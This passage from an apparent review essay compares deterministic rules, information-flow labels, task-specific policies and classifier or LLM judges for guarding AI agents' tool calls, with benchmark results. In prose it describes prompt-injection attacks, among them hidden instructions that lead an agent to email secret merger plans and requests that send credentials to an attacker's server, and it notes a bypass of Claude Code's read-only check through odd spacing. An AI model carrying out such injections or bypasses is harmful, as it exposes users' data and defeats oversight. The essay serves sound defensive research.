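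A simpler explanation than a structural limit is that the rule pack didn't target the categories that stayed the same. It covered cloud services, Kubernetes and continuous integration, while the unchanged categories were databases, software packages and monitoring. The largest gain, 30 points, was in cloud identities and secrets, as one would expect from a cloud pack. Rules about cloud permissions wouldn't catch attacks in database queries even if those attacks were easy to recognise.

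The false-positive rate supports this reading. If the structural explanation were right, new rules aimed at these categories would have caught some attacks but also stopped some harmless twins. In Yang's words, each such rule "trades a false negative for a false positive". But the pack reduced misses from 46 to 29 without adding any false alarms. In AgentTrust's engine, an added rule can't cancel an old alarm, so the 13 false alarms before and after must have been the same 13 actions. The trade-off Yang describes may well exist, but it didn't show up in this experiment, most likely because few of the new rules matched anything in the three categories.

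The name of the monitoring category, `observability_benign_hard`, suggests that many of its actions are harmless but look suspicious. If so, many of the rules' errors there were false alarms, and adding rules could not correct them because AgentTrust always applies the most severe match. The lack of improvement in this category would then come from the way AgentTrust combines its rules, and an engine that allowed exceptions might have improved.

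Yang's second piece of evidence is a "cheat" set of rules that scored only 47.6% on the 189 actions. Yang describes it as a "maximally token-stuffed rule pack" tuned to the test, but according to the methods section it consists of v1's four rules for made-up domain names such as `evil.com`. Yang wrote those rules for the older test sets, so their failure on a new one is unsurprising and isn't evidence of how high rules could score.

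The automated builds category is better evidence for Yang's view than the three zeros are. The pack was written partly for this category, yet it corrected only about 3 of the rules' 16 errors, leaving them at 48% while the judge reached 96%. In the lexical category, the rules with the pack came within one action of the judge. Yang can also point out that the 170 original rules already included some for databases, and that these scored only 29%. So the results fit the weaker claim that rules are much harder to write for some kinds of action than for others, but they don't show that writing them is impossible.

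A fairer test would put the same effort into rules for each of the eight categories, allow exceptions, and measure the results on new actions. If the rules for the semantic categories still did no better, or did better only by raising more false alarms, the structural explanation would look much stronger. No one else seems to have repeated Yang's experiment.

Work on a related task suggests that such a test would find both kinds of failure. *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* (2026) examines scanners for agent skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that people can add to an agent. It sorts the attacks that static rules missed into two groups. In the first, the attack consists of instructions in ordinary language, which static rules can't capture. In the second, the scanner had no rule for the behaviour, or its rule didn't match the way the attacker had written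 it. Writing or repairing rules could fix the second group, which accounts for 1,120 misses, counting a skill once for each scanner setup that missed it.

*A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents* (2026) describes rules for software packages, one of the three categories where Yang's results did not change. Its patterns block, among other things, package commands that skip the confirmation prompt and installations from an arbitrary version of a code repository. Each pattern is based on a documented kind of attack. Rules like these would catch some attacks that Yang's cloud pack missed. They would also block some legitimate scripts, which often skip confirmation prompts because nobody is there to answer them.

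### What better rules could read

Going by the inferred sizes, the judge gave the right verdict on 24 of the 28 database actions, so something in its input must have distinguished most of the harmful ones. It is unclear whether a fixed rule could have used that information.

Some of the information a rule needs may be in the structured fields. Yang says the parameters in each v2 record can include the destination host, target resource, scope and credentials. A rule that parses database queries could, for example, compare the destination with an approved list instead of searching the text for a suspicious phrase. Yang's experiment didn't include any rules of this kind.

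Another possibility is that the judge had an easier task. In v1, the judge's prompt contained a plain-language description of the action as well as the command. Yang doesn't print the v2 prompt. If it also included a description, and if the descriptions hinted at an action's purpose (such as "export customer records to an outside server"), the judge could classify the action from its description even when the rules had no pattern for it. The comparison would then partly reflect the difference in inputs instead of mechanisms. Running the judge on the command alone would settle this.

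Even without extra fields, a check can use a command's structure to avoid errors that have occurred in everyday use. In *Lessons Outlive Their Failures* (2026), a developer describes a guard against `git reset --hard`, a command that discards unsaved changes to code. The pattern expected `reset` to come directly after `git`, so it missed the command whenever the agent put an option between the two words. *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action* (2026) reports the opposite error, in which a guardrail held back a command that only created a new file because some of the text going into the file resembled a destructive command. A program that parses commands could avoid both errors by distinguishing the instruction from text that is only data.

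Attackers can exploit such weaknesses. *CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a vulnerability in Claude Code that let commands get past its check for read-only commands through unusual spacing and abbreviated options.

CARE, their own guardrail for shell commands, shows what a deterministic check can achieve by parsing. Like AgentTrust, it first rewrites the command into a standard form. It then builds a syntax tree, a representation of the command's programs, arguments and files and the connections between them. AgentTrust's normalizer doesn't build one. Yang left a full parser for a later version because of its complexity and the temptation to run parts of the command for better coverage.

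From the tree, CARE computes four scores between 0 and 1: one for the kind of command, one for the files it touches, one for matches with known dangerous patterns, and one for suspicious structure. It combines them in a weighted sum:

score = w₁ · command + w₂ · files + w₃ · patterns + w₄ · structure

The weights add up to 1. CARE allows commands with low scores, blocks those with high scores, and issues a warning for those in between. The full version resolves these warnings with further checks and, if necessary, a language model. In AgentTrust a single matching rule can decide the verdict, whereas in CARE several weak signs can add up to a high score.

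CARE's score for a file depends on what the command does with it. Reading `/etc/os-release`, a system file that names the installed version of Linux, gets a low score, while adding a line to `/etc/profile`, which runs whenever someone logs in, gets a high one. A pattern that matched every path beginning with `/etc/` would treat the two alike. CARE also raises the score for reading files that contain secrets, because reading a secret can be the first step in stealing it.

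Liu and colleagues measure performance with the F1 score, which combines precision (the share of blocked commands that really are dangerous) and recall (the share of dangerous commands that the check blocks):

F1 = 2 · precision · recall / (precision + recall)

On the main test set, CARE without a language model reached an F1 score of 84.99% and took 0.34 milliseconds on average. The best of the other rule-based checks reached 72.62%. Adding the language model for uncertain commands raised CARE's score only to 85.64%, with a false-positive rate of 0.91%.

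So the rule-based checks that CARE competed with had a lot of room for improvement, and most of the gain didn't require a language model. But these are shell commands, many of which are obviously dangerous, and the result may not carry over to database queries or software packages. If half the commands in the test set are dangerous, as the word "balanced" suggests, an F1 score of 85.64% with so few false alarms means that CARE still misses about a quarter of the dangerous ones.

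Some of those misses may be unavoidable for any check that has only CARE's inputs. CARE receives one command at a time, along with facts about the file system such as the location of the agent's working folder, but not the user's request or anything the agent did earlier.

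## Deterministic rules that track context and data flow

CARE checks one command at a time, but a context rule can also use records of earlier actions and of where data came from. If such rules can separate Yang's twin pairs, then many semantic threats need better records rather than a language model that judges meaning. This is probably the most serious objection to the split between lexical and semantic threats, and several research groups have built systems that test it.

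### How data gets a label and keeps it

A program can keep such records with information-flow labels, which computer security researchers developed in the 1970s. A label is a note that the program attaches to a piece of data. An origin label might be "trusted" for the user's request and "untrusted" for a web page. A sensitivity label might be "public", "internal" or "secret". The program stores the labels outside the model, so nothing the model reads or writes can change them.

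An administrator decides which sources get which labels, for example that every file in a credentials folder is secret. After that, labels spread by a fixed formula. Anything the agent produces from several inputs gets the highest sensitivity and the lowest trust among them:

sensitivity(output) = max of sensitivity(input)

trust(output) = min of trust(input)

Before an agent sends data, the guardrail checks the destination's clearance, which is the most sensitive data the destination may receive, and blocks the data if its sensitivity is higher. A summary of a public report and a secret salary file counts as secret, even if it doesn't mention any salaries.

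*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) describes a guardrail called FORGE that applies this idea to agents. FORGE records every message, tool call and tool result as an event and links it to the later events it may have influenced, forming a graph of possible causes. Its policies are rules written in Datalog, a database language in which any question about a finite set of facts has a definite answer.

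In their main example, a user asks an agent to summarise a vendor's document and email the summary. The document contains a hidden instruction to send internal data to an outsider. FORGE handles the attack as follows:

1. The agent reads the vendor's document. It came from outside, so FORGE labels it untrusted.
2. The agent follows the hidden instruction and reads an internal file, which FORGE labels sensitive.
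3. The agent proposes an email to an external address. The model wrote the email after reading both documents, so the graph links both to the email.
4. Two rules pass the labels along these links. An event is tainted if it is untrusted or depends on a tainted event, and it carries a secret if it is sensitive or depends on an event that carries a secret. The email gets both labels.
5. A last rule denies any external message that has both labels, so the email never leaves.

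The two rules in step 4 are recursive. They also apply to their own results, so a label can pass through any number of steps, including from one agent to another. An attacker gains nothing by having the agent translate or encode the secret first, because the rules don't depend on the email's wording and the new copy is still derived from the original.

FORGE can't determine which parts of its input a model used, so it treats every message in the model's history as an influence on the next one. This is cautious, but after the agent reads a single secret file, everything it writes carries that file's label.

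Palumbo and colleagues first tried the rules on a similar attack, in which the hidden instruction posed as a mandatory compliance audit. An agent based on GPT-4.1-mini, protected only by a prompt telling it not to leak data, emailed top-secret merger plans to the attacker in all five runs. With the label rules, it never sent them, and it still completed a harmless summary task all five times. Five runs of one attack show that the mechanism works, but not how often it would fail on other attacks.

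### Yang's twin pairs under a flow rule

A flow rule can distinguish the two `curl` requests in Yang's telemetry pair, however similar the commands look. It allows the request that sends usage figures to the team's own server, because the figures aren't sensitive. It denies the request that sends cloud credentials to the thief's server, because the credentials are secret and that server has no clearance.

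But the agent may never read the credentials itself, because `curl` can open a file and send it in a single command. In that case, no earlier "read" event exists to supply the label, so the guardrail has to parse the command, find the file it names and look up that file's label. FORGE lets policy authors call outside functions to do this, but someone has to write those functions.

A list of approved hosts fails on Yang's harder version, where the thief's storage is on an approved service, because the list approves each host for every kind of data. With labels, the organisation can approve a service for build reports but not for credentials. Cloud credentials rarely belong in an upload, so the rule can block them regardless of who owns the storage location. For customer records, the rule has to check ownership, because the company may well back them up to the same service. It could do this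 using a list of the company's own accounts.

Fixed rules can tell the two versions in this pair apart if they have the right facts. Yang's claim that they can't holds only for rules that lack those facts.

Labels are less useful when someone has a legitimate reason to release sensitive data. Suppose an outside lawyer emails a user to ask for a confidential contract, and the user tells the agent to send it. FORGE's rule denies the message because the contract is secret, the lawyer's email is untrusted and the recipient is external. An attacker's email asking for the same contract would produce the same labels, even though the user agreed only to the lawyer's request. A guardrail could show the user the recipient and the attachment, then store the confirmation for a fixed rule to use, but then a human is making the decision. To decide without asking, the guardrail has to interpret the ordinary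 language of the user's original request and determine whether it covers this contract and this recipient.

Labels also can't show whether an agent runs `kubectl get secret` for an engineer or for an attacker. A flow rule can let the agent read the password in the secret but block the agent from sending it outside the system. But the rule doesn't apply if the agent uses the password to log in to an internal database and delete records, because the password never leaves the system.

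The rule also interferes with the engineer's work. After reading the password, the agent might search the web for an error message. If web searches count as external messages, FORGE's rule allows the first search because the agent hasn't read anything untrusted yet. The search results are untrusted, so the rule denies a second search.

The rule also fits the incidents in Anthropic's log poorly, because it requires an untrusted source and those incidents involved no attacker. It would have let an agent upload an engineer's GitHub token to an internal cluster. A stricter rule that allows a token to go only to the service that issued it would have stopped the upload. No label rule would have prevented the branch deletions, because deleting a branch doesn't send data anywhere.

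### The cost in completed tasks

Palumbo and colleagues measured the downsides of two policies on AgentDojo, the benchmark of prompt injection attacks that Ray also used. They tested a GPT-4o agent on 97 tasks without an attack and in 949 runs with one, and repeated the whole set five times.

They took one policy from FIDES, a 2025 information-flow system. It blocks any consequential call once the agent has untrusted content in its context, and it blocks the disclosure of confidential data to an unauthorised destination. Their own "provenance policy" checks, separately for each call, whether the user asked for this kind of effect and whether the target, such as the recipient of a payment, came from an acceptable source. Under this policy, an agent that has read a suspicious email can still pay a bill.

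In the following results, every version of the agent also had a defence that repeats the user's request after each batch of tool outputs. The tool filter is a list of allowed tools that a language model chooses based on the user's request.

| Additional check | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% |
| Tool filter | 73.4% | 69.5% | 3.1% |
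| FIDES policy in FORGE | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.6% |
| Provenance policy in FORGE | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.9% |

The FIDES policy prevented the agent from completing 60% of the tasks it could otherwise complete. This would be expected if most useful work involves reading something untrusted and then acting on it. The original FIDES can also hide tool results from the model, so it may do better than its policy does inside FORGE.

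The provenance policy kept three quarters of the completed tasks, but the tool filter is a strong alternative. The policy stopped about 21 more attacks out of 949 than the filter, but its task completion rate without attacks was 11 percentage points lower. The added protection may be worth that loss for an agent that moves money but not for one that books restaurants.

AgentDojo counts some attacks as successful when the agent merely attempts the harmful call. Under the provenance policy, 0.2% of attacks actually took effect. These attacks worked through the agent's final written answer, which FORGE doesn't check.

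A fixed rule doesn't always reduce the number of completed tasks. FORGE also enforced business rules on τ²-bench, a benchmark in which agents handle customer service for an airline and a shop. Across three frontier models, average success rose from 74.7% to 81.5% on airline tasks and from 86.3% to 87.4% on retail tasks. FORGE explains each denial to the agent, which can then correct its mistake, for instance by getting the customer's consent before trying again. The explanation helps when an acceptable alternative exists, but not when the only way to complete a task is to act on an untrusted document.

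### Why put the boundary outside the model?

Bhattarai and Vu (2026), in *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, argue that training alone can never guarantee that a model will keep track of where its instructions came from. A model receives its developer's instructions, the user's request and any retrieved documents as one stream of text. The markers that separate them are also text, which an attacker can imitate. Any method the model learns for telling commands from data therefore depends on content that the attacker partly controls, so some input will have a nonzero chance of making the model treat data as a command.

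They compare this to SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a website form. Filters for suspicious words reduced the problem but didn't end it. The reliable solution was to send the query and the user's input to the database through separate channels.

Bhattarai and Vu call their result a theorem, but they only sketch a proof, and the sketch largely assumes that the attacker can find a working input. Their conclusion that the failure rate is above zero is also weak, since a rate of one in a billion would satisfy it. They do make a good case that training alone offers no guarantee, which matters when an attacker can try thousands of variations. As they point out, the argument applies equally to a model judge that reads the same mixed text.

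In their alternative, the model chooses from a fixed list of action types. A separate program decides whether to allow the action, using facts such as the user's identity and the data's labels, and a trusted adapter carries it out. Their example labels form a single scale from "untrusted" through "internal" to "confidential", so a document that is both untrusted and confidential, such as a contract from another company, has no natural place on it. FORGE avoids this problem by tracking trust and confidentiality separately.

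Bhattarai and Vu limit their claim to authorisation, meaning that the agent can't do what the policy forbids, so a user who is allowed to send email can still send a harmful one. Their argument covers where to enforce a policy but not how to choose the right one for a particular task.

### Policies written for a single task

A general-purpose assistant needs different permissions for different requests. *Sapien* (Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tool that sends money, which the agent needs if the user writes "refund the person who sent me money last week" but not if the user asks for a summary of their inbox. A fixed policy has to either allow payments during the inbox summary or forbid the refund.

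Two designs from 2025 had already tried to adapt the rules to the request. In CaMeL, by Debenedetti and colleagues, a language model turns the request into a fixed plan without seeing any untrusted content. Injected text can then alter the data passing through the plan, but not the plan's steps. CaMeL also restricts which data can go where. According to Tiffany and colleagues, CaMeL is limited to single requests because the plan has to carry out the whole task by itself.

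Progent, by Shi and colleagues, lets the agent choose its own steps but sets conditions on each tool, such as which arguments it may receive. A developer can set these rules in advance, or a model can generate them from the user's request and revise them after a tool call. Tiffany and colleagues object that the revisions rely on tool outputs, which could let injected text influence the rules. They aren't neutral critics, because their own system competes with both designs.

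*LEANGUARD* reports an independent test of Progent on τ²-bench with five Qwen models. Agents broke a formal version of the benchmark's rules in 36 of 1,390 episodes with Progent and in 28 without any guardrail, a difference that could easily be chance. Task success fell from 72.7% to 66.9% with Progent. Most of the violations were steps in the wrong order or actions that didn't fit the current state of the records, which conditions on single calls are poorly suited to catch. τ²-bench has no attackers, so these results are only weak evidence of how well Progent stops prompt injection.

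Sapien, a system by Tiffany and colleagues at Google, also has a model write the policy. The model sees only the user's request and the tool documentation, so injected text can't reach it. A Sapien policy describes permitted sequences of calls and can refer to earlier results, unlike a plain list of tools. For the refund, the policy would require the agent to list the transactions first. The agent could then pay only someone who had sent money in the past week, and only the amount that person had sent.

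Sapien enforces the policy by turning it into a finite automaton, a diagram of states with arrows for the calls permitted in each state. It stores the results of completed calls and checks each proposed call against the currently available arrows. If none fits, it refuses the call and tells the agent which condition failed. The model helps write the rules, but ordinary code enforces most of them.

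If the user asks the agent to carry out a to-do list on a web page, nobody can write the full policy in advance. Sapien lets the agent fetch the page, then generates the missing part of the policy from its contents. This is reasonable because the user chose to let the page determine the tasks, but anyone who can edit the page can also set those tasks. A policy can also include a narrow check by a model, such as whether an email faithfully summarises a document. An attacker might fool this check, but the fixed conditions on the recipient and the tool would still hold.

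Tiffany and colleagues used an unusually strict security test. They assumed that an attacker already controls the agent and can fool every model check that reads untrusted text, and they checked whether any sequence of calls that the policy permits would achieve the attacker's goal. Across four recent models, Sapien's policies ruled out 93% to 95% of 949 attacks on AgentDojo, compared with 83% to 87% for a list of allowed tools. For Toolathlon, a benchmark of longer tasks, they wrote 212 attacks that exploit the tools each task needs. With Gemini 3.8 Flash, Sapien ruled out 65% of these, compared with 32% for the tool list.

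The attacks that remained possible are directly relevant to Yang's claim. Tiffany and colleagues classify more than four fifths of them as semantic, meaning that no deterministic condition could tell the harmful behaviour from the harmless. In one, the agent summarises interview feedback and the attacker wants it to turn a rejection into a "strong hire". In another, the agent plans a walking route across a campus and the attacker wants the route to go through dangerous construction sites. The policy can specify which file the agent writes, but it can't determine whether the content is right.

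This is arguably better evidence for a semantic category than Yang's own experiment, because it shows which attacks still succeed after a serious attempt to use context. The category is also narrower than Yang's, consisting mainly of false or harmful content and tasks that hand control to an untrusted source. Fixed rules can stop much ordinary data theft. Some attacks in the category can't be stopped by any check on tool calls. A single AgentDojo goal, which is only to make the agent output a certain sentence, accounts for 36% of the successful attacks on that benchmark.

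Sapien's policies only slightly reduced the number of tasks agents completed, by between one and five of the 97 on AgentDojo. Some tasks failed because the model had written a policy that did not match the data. One policy required "London Luxury Hotel", the name in the user's request, but the database had "London Luxury". The delay was a bigger drawback. Writing a policy took between 43 and 100 seconds per AgentDojo task, which was most of the total running time. On the longer Toolathlon tasks, Sapien raised the average running time from 548 to 679 seconds.

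These losses are much smaller than FORGE's on the same benchmark, probably in part because a policy for one task can permit exactly what that task needs. But the agents also used newer models than GPT-4o, so the difference can't be attributed to the policies alone. The security figures aren't comparable, because FORGE's are for attacks that worked in practice and Sapien's are for attacks that the policy would permit.

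### Where a rule and a judge disagreed

*LEANGUARD* makes it possible to compare fixed rules with a model judge on the same calls. Its rules allow a call under this condition:

allow = (some permit holds) and (every requirement holds) and (no prohibition holds) and (no check ends in an error)

A requirement can depend on earlier events, such as the agent having looked up an order before changing it. The facts used to check requirements come from the company's database and a log of earlier events, never from the agent's own statements. The rules are written in Lean, a programming language that can check mathematical proofs, and a proof shows that the program's decisions match the formal meaning of the policy.

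On τ²-bench, unguarded agents executed at least 33 calls that the policy forbids, while guarded agents executed none, as the design guarantees. Guarded agents that received an explanation after each denial succeeded on 70.9% of tasks, compared with 72.7% for unguarded agents, a difference that could be due to chance.

A model judge, Qwen3.8-27B, then looked for executed calls that broke the benchmark's written policy. It flagged 182 calls in the guarded runs, and the rules had allowed all of them.

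| What the disagreement was about | Calls |
|---|---|
| Whether the customer had agreed to an action that requires confirmation | 71 |
| Facts that the rules used and the judge couldn't see | 37 |
| Behaviour for which the formal policy had no rule | 69 |
| Calls that only read data | 5 |

In the 37 cases about facts, the rules used better information than the judge had. For instance, they allowed roaming on a phone line because the records showed that the line was abroad, which the judge couldn't tell from the conversation. A judge with those records might well have agreed, so these cases show the value of the records more than a weakness of judges.

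The 71 disputes about consent are harder to settle. The judge read the conversation, whereas the rules relied on a stored confirmation and would apply it even if it was false. Another language model produced the confirmations in this experiment, and an audit found that some were wrong. In one, the recorded approval did not reflect a payment limit that the customer had set.

The other large group consists of 69 calls that the judge flagged for behaviour no formal rule covered. Of these, 23 transferred the customer to a human, which the written policy restricts but the formal policy doesn't mention. Another 23 concerned the order in which the agent handled the customer's requests. The written policy doesn't regulate that either, so the judge was probably wrong to flag them. The audit also found missing rules that would be easy to add, such as a limit on the total extra data a customer can buy.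 A judge can help find such gaps even if its verdicts are too unreliable to enforce.

### Consistently wrong rules, and the people who write them

*ToolGuardian* states that "determinism is not the same as correctness", and its experiments include an example. Before an agent may use a tool, the system collects evidence about it and applies fixed rules to decide whether to admit it. The test set had eight harmless tools and eight malicious ones.

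Using evidence from the tools' descriptions and trial runs, the rules rejected six of the malicious tools and none of the eight harmless ones, although they restricted all eight. Adding source code analysis led them to reject seven malicious tools, but also two harmless ones. One was a terminal controller, whose code can start other programs and capture the screen. The rules will always reject this tool, even though a legitimate administrator needs those abilities.

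A language model given the same structured evidence in place of the rules also rejected two harmless tools, including the terminal controller. In a separate test of 20 tasks and workflows, the logical rules, an ordinary hand-coded program and the model all gave the right verdict every time. These perfect scores are less impressive because the same researchers designed the scenarios and the policy together. When they removed the explicit rules from the model's prompt, it got only 15 right, so the model also depended on a well-written policy.

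Writing that policy takes a lot of work. *ToolGuardian* reports that the main burden is designing rules and exceptions, not computing time. For the three customer service domains, *LEANGUARD* needed 45 rules in 583 lines of code, which a language model drafted and people corrected. FORGE's users can also have a model translate a written policy. Palumbo and colleagues recommend checking that every requirement has a rule and that every rule has a basis in the original text, because a formal guarantee is useless if the translation is wrong. Sapien doesn't need a human to write the policy, but it also doesn't require a human to check the policy before it takes effect.

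Someone also has to keep the permissions up to date. *LEANGUARD* shows what can happen if nobody does, using DTap, a benchmark with attacks in domains such as travel, finance and medicine. The agent was allowed to read records but not to change anything. The success rate of direct attacks fell from 57.9% to 5.9%, but the share of harmless tasks completed also fell, from 53.1% to 12.5%. Of the 1,918 harmless tasks that agents completed only without the guard, 992 failed because it blocked patient registration, and 810 because they needed a change that nobody had authorised. In telecom, where tasks rarely involve changes, the attack success rate fell from 55.1% to 2.4% and the agents completed as many tasks as before.

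These rules also work best with narrow tools. A payment tool's effect is clear from its arguments, such as the amount and recipient, but a shell command can do almost anything. On DTap, the guard stopped 5,792 calls because it couldn't determine what they would do, and nearly half were general shell commands. For the Toolathlon tests, Tiffany and colleagues disabled a tool that runs Python code and required Sapien's policies to specify which terminal commands the agent could use. Code that opens its own network connection can similarly bypass the points FORGE monitors.

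Rules that track data flow are a strong alternative to a model judge for an agent that issues refunds or sends email through dedicated tools. For a coding agent with a shell, they first need a parser that can reliably work out which files a command reads and where it sends them. Most of Yang's examples are shell commands, so this requirement limits the objection to Yang's split.

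## Classifiers and language-model judges

A context rule can use only facts that a program has stored in a form the rule can look up. For a coding agent, much of the relevant information exists only in ordinary language, such as the user's request, an error message or the agent's explanation of its plan. A classifier or model judge can take all of this as input along with the command.

Classifiers and language-model judges are both usually language models, but developers define what counts as dangerous differently for each. They train a classifier on labelled examples, adjusting its weights until its labels mostly match those in the examples. They give a judge written instructions along with every action it evaluates.

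### Classifiers trained on agents' actions

In 2023, Meta released Llama Guard, a 7-billion-parameter language model that screens chat messages. Yang points out that its classification of `rm -rf /` depends on the surrounding text, not on the fact that the deletion is irreversible.

Researchers call such classifiers guard models. *Agent Safety From Within* (2026) defines a guard model as an auxiliary model specialised for safety that assesses another model's inputs or outputs without modifying that model. Most guard models write out a label, but the paper's method computes a safety score from internal states, the numbers a model computes as it processes text.

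Newer guard models take an agent's tool calls as input. *ToolSafe* (2026) describes TS-Guard, which receives the user's request, the session history and the proposed call. It writes a short analysis and then makes three judgements in a single pass: whether the request is harmful, whether the call is linked to a third-party attack, and whether the call is safe. The first two help with the third because they cover two common reasons a call is unsafe.

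Training such a model takes many examples of dangerous actions, which are rare in real use. In *StepGuard*, Zheng, Li and colleagues (2026) simulate them. They start with a run in which the agent takes a dangerous action at a known step. They keep everything before that step and generate two new endings, one in which the agent refuses and one in which it finds a safe way to continue. They also generate a harmless run with the same tools, so that the classifier can't just learn that certain tools are dangerous.

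The alternative endings share a history but differ in the action. This is almost the reverse of Yang's twin pairs, which show the same or nearly the same action in different circumstances. The harmless run with the same tools is closer to Yang's pairs.

Zheng and colleagues first trained a 4-billion-parameter model on 3,000 of these examples, after which it flagged too many harmless actions. They then used reinforcement learning, in which the model produces several answers and training favours those with higher rewards:

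reward = 0.5 · (verdict correct) + 0.5 · (verdict and type of risk both correct)

Each bracket counts as 1 if true and 0 if false. The training also gives more weight to whichever actions, safe or unsafe, the model is currently judging less accurately. With this weighting, the gap between the model's accuracy on safe and unsafe actions was 8 points, compared with 13 for the same method without it.

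The following accuracies come from their tests, which cover both completed runs and single actions that have not yet happened.

| Model | Type | Completed runs | Single actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama Guard 3, 8B | Classifier for chat | 46.5% | 77.6% |
| Qwen3Guard, 8B | Classifier for chat | 54.7% | 75.6% |
| AgentDoG, 4B | Classifier for completed agent runs | 74.1% | 52.5% |
| TS-Guard, 7B | Classifier for single agent actions | 71.5% | 84.0% |
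| StepGuard, 4B | Classifier for both | 83.0% | 84.8% |
| Qwen3-4B-Instruct | General model | 70.5% | 79.3% |
| GPT-5.4 | General model | 83.0% | 81.3% |

StepGuard started as a version of Qwen3-4B-Instruct, so the training seems to have added about 12 points on completed runs and 5 on single actions. Those gains were enough for the small model to match GPT-5.4 on these tests.

The chat classifiers' scores on single actions look good only because they average two very different tests. One test, judging by its name, comes from AgentDojo, where the danger lies in injected instructions. Qwen3Guard's F1 score there was zero, which means it caught practically none of the dangerous actions. Its accuracy was still about 71% because most of the actions were harmless. The other test appears to come from AgentHarm, where the user asks for something harmful. The chat classifiers scored between 80% and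 82% on it, ahead of StepGuard (74%) and GPT-5.4 (69%). They can recognise a harmful request, but they miss ordinary-looking actions that serve an attacker.

AgentDoG's results show how closely a classifier can depend on the form of its training data. *AgentDoG* (2026) describes a model trained to diagnose completed runs. The model did little better than chance on single actions, but in *Benchmarks for Trajectory Safety Evaluation and Diagnosis in OpenClaw and Codex* (2026) it reached 87.2% accuracy on completed runs of OpenClaw, an open-source agent. That test has 204 safe and 296 unsafe runs, according to *AgentDoG 1.5* (2026), and AgentDoG caught 92.9% of the unsafe ones. Together, these figures imply that it wrongly flagged 43 of the safe runs, or 21%. In the same comparison, most other guard models did worse than general models, and the guard models' results fell most on runs of Codex,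 OpenAI's coding agent.

In use, a guard model also affects how many tasks the agent completes. Zheng and colleagues put StepGuard in front of an agent on AgentDojo and a similar benchmark, AgentDyn. The average attack success rate fell by 77% relative to no guard, while the average task completion rate fell by only 2.8 percentage points. FORGE's provenance policy lowered task completion by much more on AgentDojo, 21 points, although the agents were different. Nearly a quarter of the previously successful attacks still worked with StepGuard, however, and a classifier can't guarantee which attacks it will stop.

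### Judges that follow written instructions

A model judge doesn't need training examples. If a company changes its storage provider, someone can update the judge by editing a sentence in its instructions. A classifier trained to accept the old provider may need retraining on new examples, but it is usually cheaper to run, since a model with 4 billion parameters fits on a single ordinary graphics card.

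Judges and some newer classifiers can also explain their verdicts. For example, the classifier StepGuard outputs the type of risk, the unsafe step and the reason that step is unsafe. An explanation helps a person review the decision, but it is also generated text and may not reflect how the model reached the verdict.

Yang gave five models the same prompt and ran each alone to see what judges can do without rules. The external set is the one where the rules' accuracy fell to 48.1%. The abbreviations stand for the false-positive and false-negative rates.

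| Check | External set: accuracy | FPR | FNR | 630 actions: accuracy | FPR | FNR |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Rules | 48.1% | 22.4% | 52.9% | 95.4% | 2.1% | 6.1% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 85.2% | 1.7% | 4.6% | 91.0% | 1.6% | 9.9% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 84.1% | 0.0% | 2.3% | 89.7% | 1.1% | 7.8% |
| GPT-5.5 | 83.6% | 6.9% | 1.1% | 76.2% | 19.7% | 1.7% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 75.7% | 0.0% | 11.5% | 80.0% | 0.0% | 12.2% |
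| DeepSeek | 69.8% | 31.0% | 5.7% | 87.1% | 1.6% | 8.1% |

On the external set, every judge beat the rules by more than 20 points. The top three were within three correct verdicts of each other, so their order means little. Four of the five judges also raised far fewer false alarms than the rules. The exception was DeepSeek, which Yang included as a weak baseline.

On the 630 actions, every judge did worse than the rules. The comparison favours the rules, because Yang added some rules after seeing actions from this set. Yang attributes most of the gap to actions that deserve a warning, where the correct verdict is partly subjective. That explanation fits Sonnet 4.6 well, since it made about 36 more errors than the rules and only 6 of the extra errors were dangerous actions that it let run. For Opus 4.8, 13 of the 28 extra errors were dangerous actions that it let run, so nearly half of its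 gap is more serious than a disagreement about warnings.

GPT-5.5 made a different trade-off from the Claude models. On the 630 actions, it let about 6 of 344 dangerous ones run, compared with 27 for Sonnet, but it flagged about 37 of 188 harmless ones, compared with 2 for Sonnet. GPT-5.5 may simply have a lower threshold for flagging actions, so these results don't show which model is better at telling dangerous actions from harmless ones.

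None of the judges blocked a harmless action, so all their false positives were warnings or requests for review. Each judge evaluated about 380 harmless actions across Yang's three test sets. In a sample that size, zero blocks is compatible with a true wrongful-block rate of up to about 0.8%, or one in every 125 harmless actions.

### Do stronger models only reduce false alarms?

Yang takes these results to show that, in general, "capability buys precision, not recall". By precision, Yang means a low false-positive rate. On this view, even the smallest model catches the semantic attacks that rules miss, and a larger model mainly raises fewer false alarms.

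The table contradicts this. On the external set, Haiku 4.5 had no false positives, so a larger model couldn't have fewer. But it missed 11.5% of the dangerous actions (about 10 of 87), while Sonnet missed 2.3% (about 2). The difference is only eight actions, but it is unlikely to be chance because both models judged the same ones. On the 630 actions, Haiku again had no false positives and had the highest miss rate of any judge.

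Some of Yang's other results fit the claim. On the older set of 300 actions, the false-positive rate fell from 6.8% for Haiku to 3.0% for Sonnet and zero for Opus, while the miss rate rose slightly, from 4.7% for Haiku to 7.0% for Sonnet and 7.8% for Opus. DeepSeek's results on the external set also fit, with a false-positive rate of 31.0% and a miss rate close to that of Opus. So a weaker judge may raise more false alarms or miss more attacks, and which it does can vary by test set.

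Haiku had ten misses and no false alarms on the external set, so an operator who used it as a judge could not fix its errors by filtering out false alarms afterwards. Using a cheap model and filtering its alarms would work if small models caught everything.

### Calibration and the confidence gate

Yang's filter for false alarms is a confidence gate. For each verdict, AgentTrust v2 compares the judge's confidence with a threshold, τ. When the judge supplements the rules, the gate works as follows:

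- If the judge's verdict is stricter than the rules' verdict and its confidence is at least τ, the judge's verdict applies.
- Otherwise, the rules' verdict stands.

A judge's confidence is a number that the model writes, so it may not match how often the model is right. A judge is calibrated if the two match, so that about 80% of the verdicts it gives with a confidence of 0.8 are correct.

A gate needs a judge that is more confident when it is right than when it is wrong, but the judge doesn't strictly need to be calibrated. Suppose a judge assigns 0.85 confidence to every verdict and is right 85% of the time. It is perfectly calibrated, but any threshold would accept either all its verdicts or none. Another judge might assign 0.99 whenever it is right and 0.95 whenever it is wrong. It is badly calibrated, but a threshold of 0.97 would remove every error.

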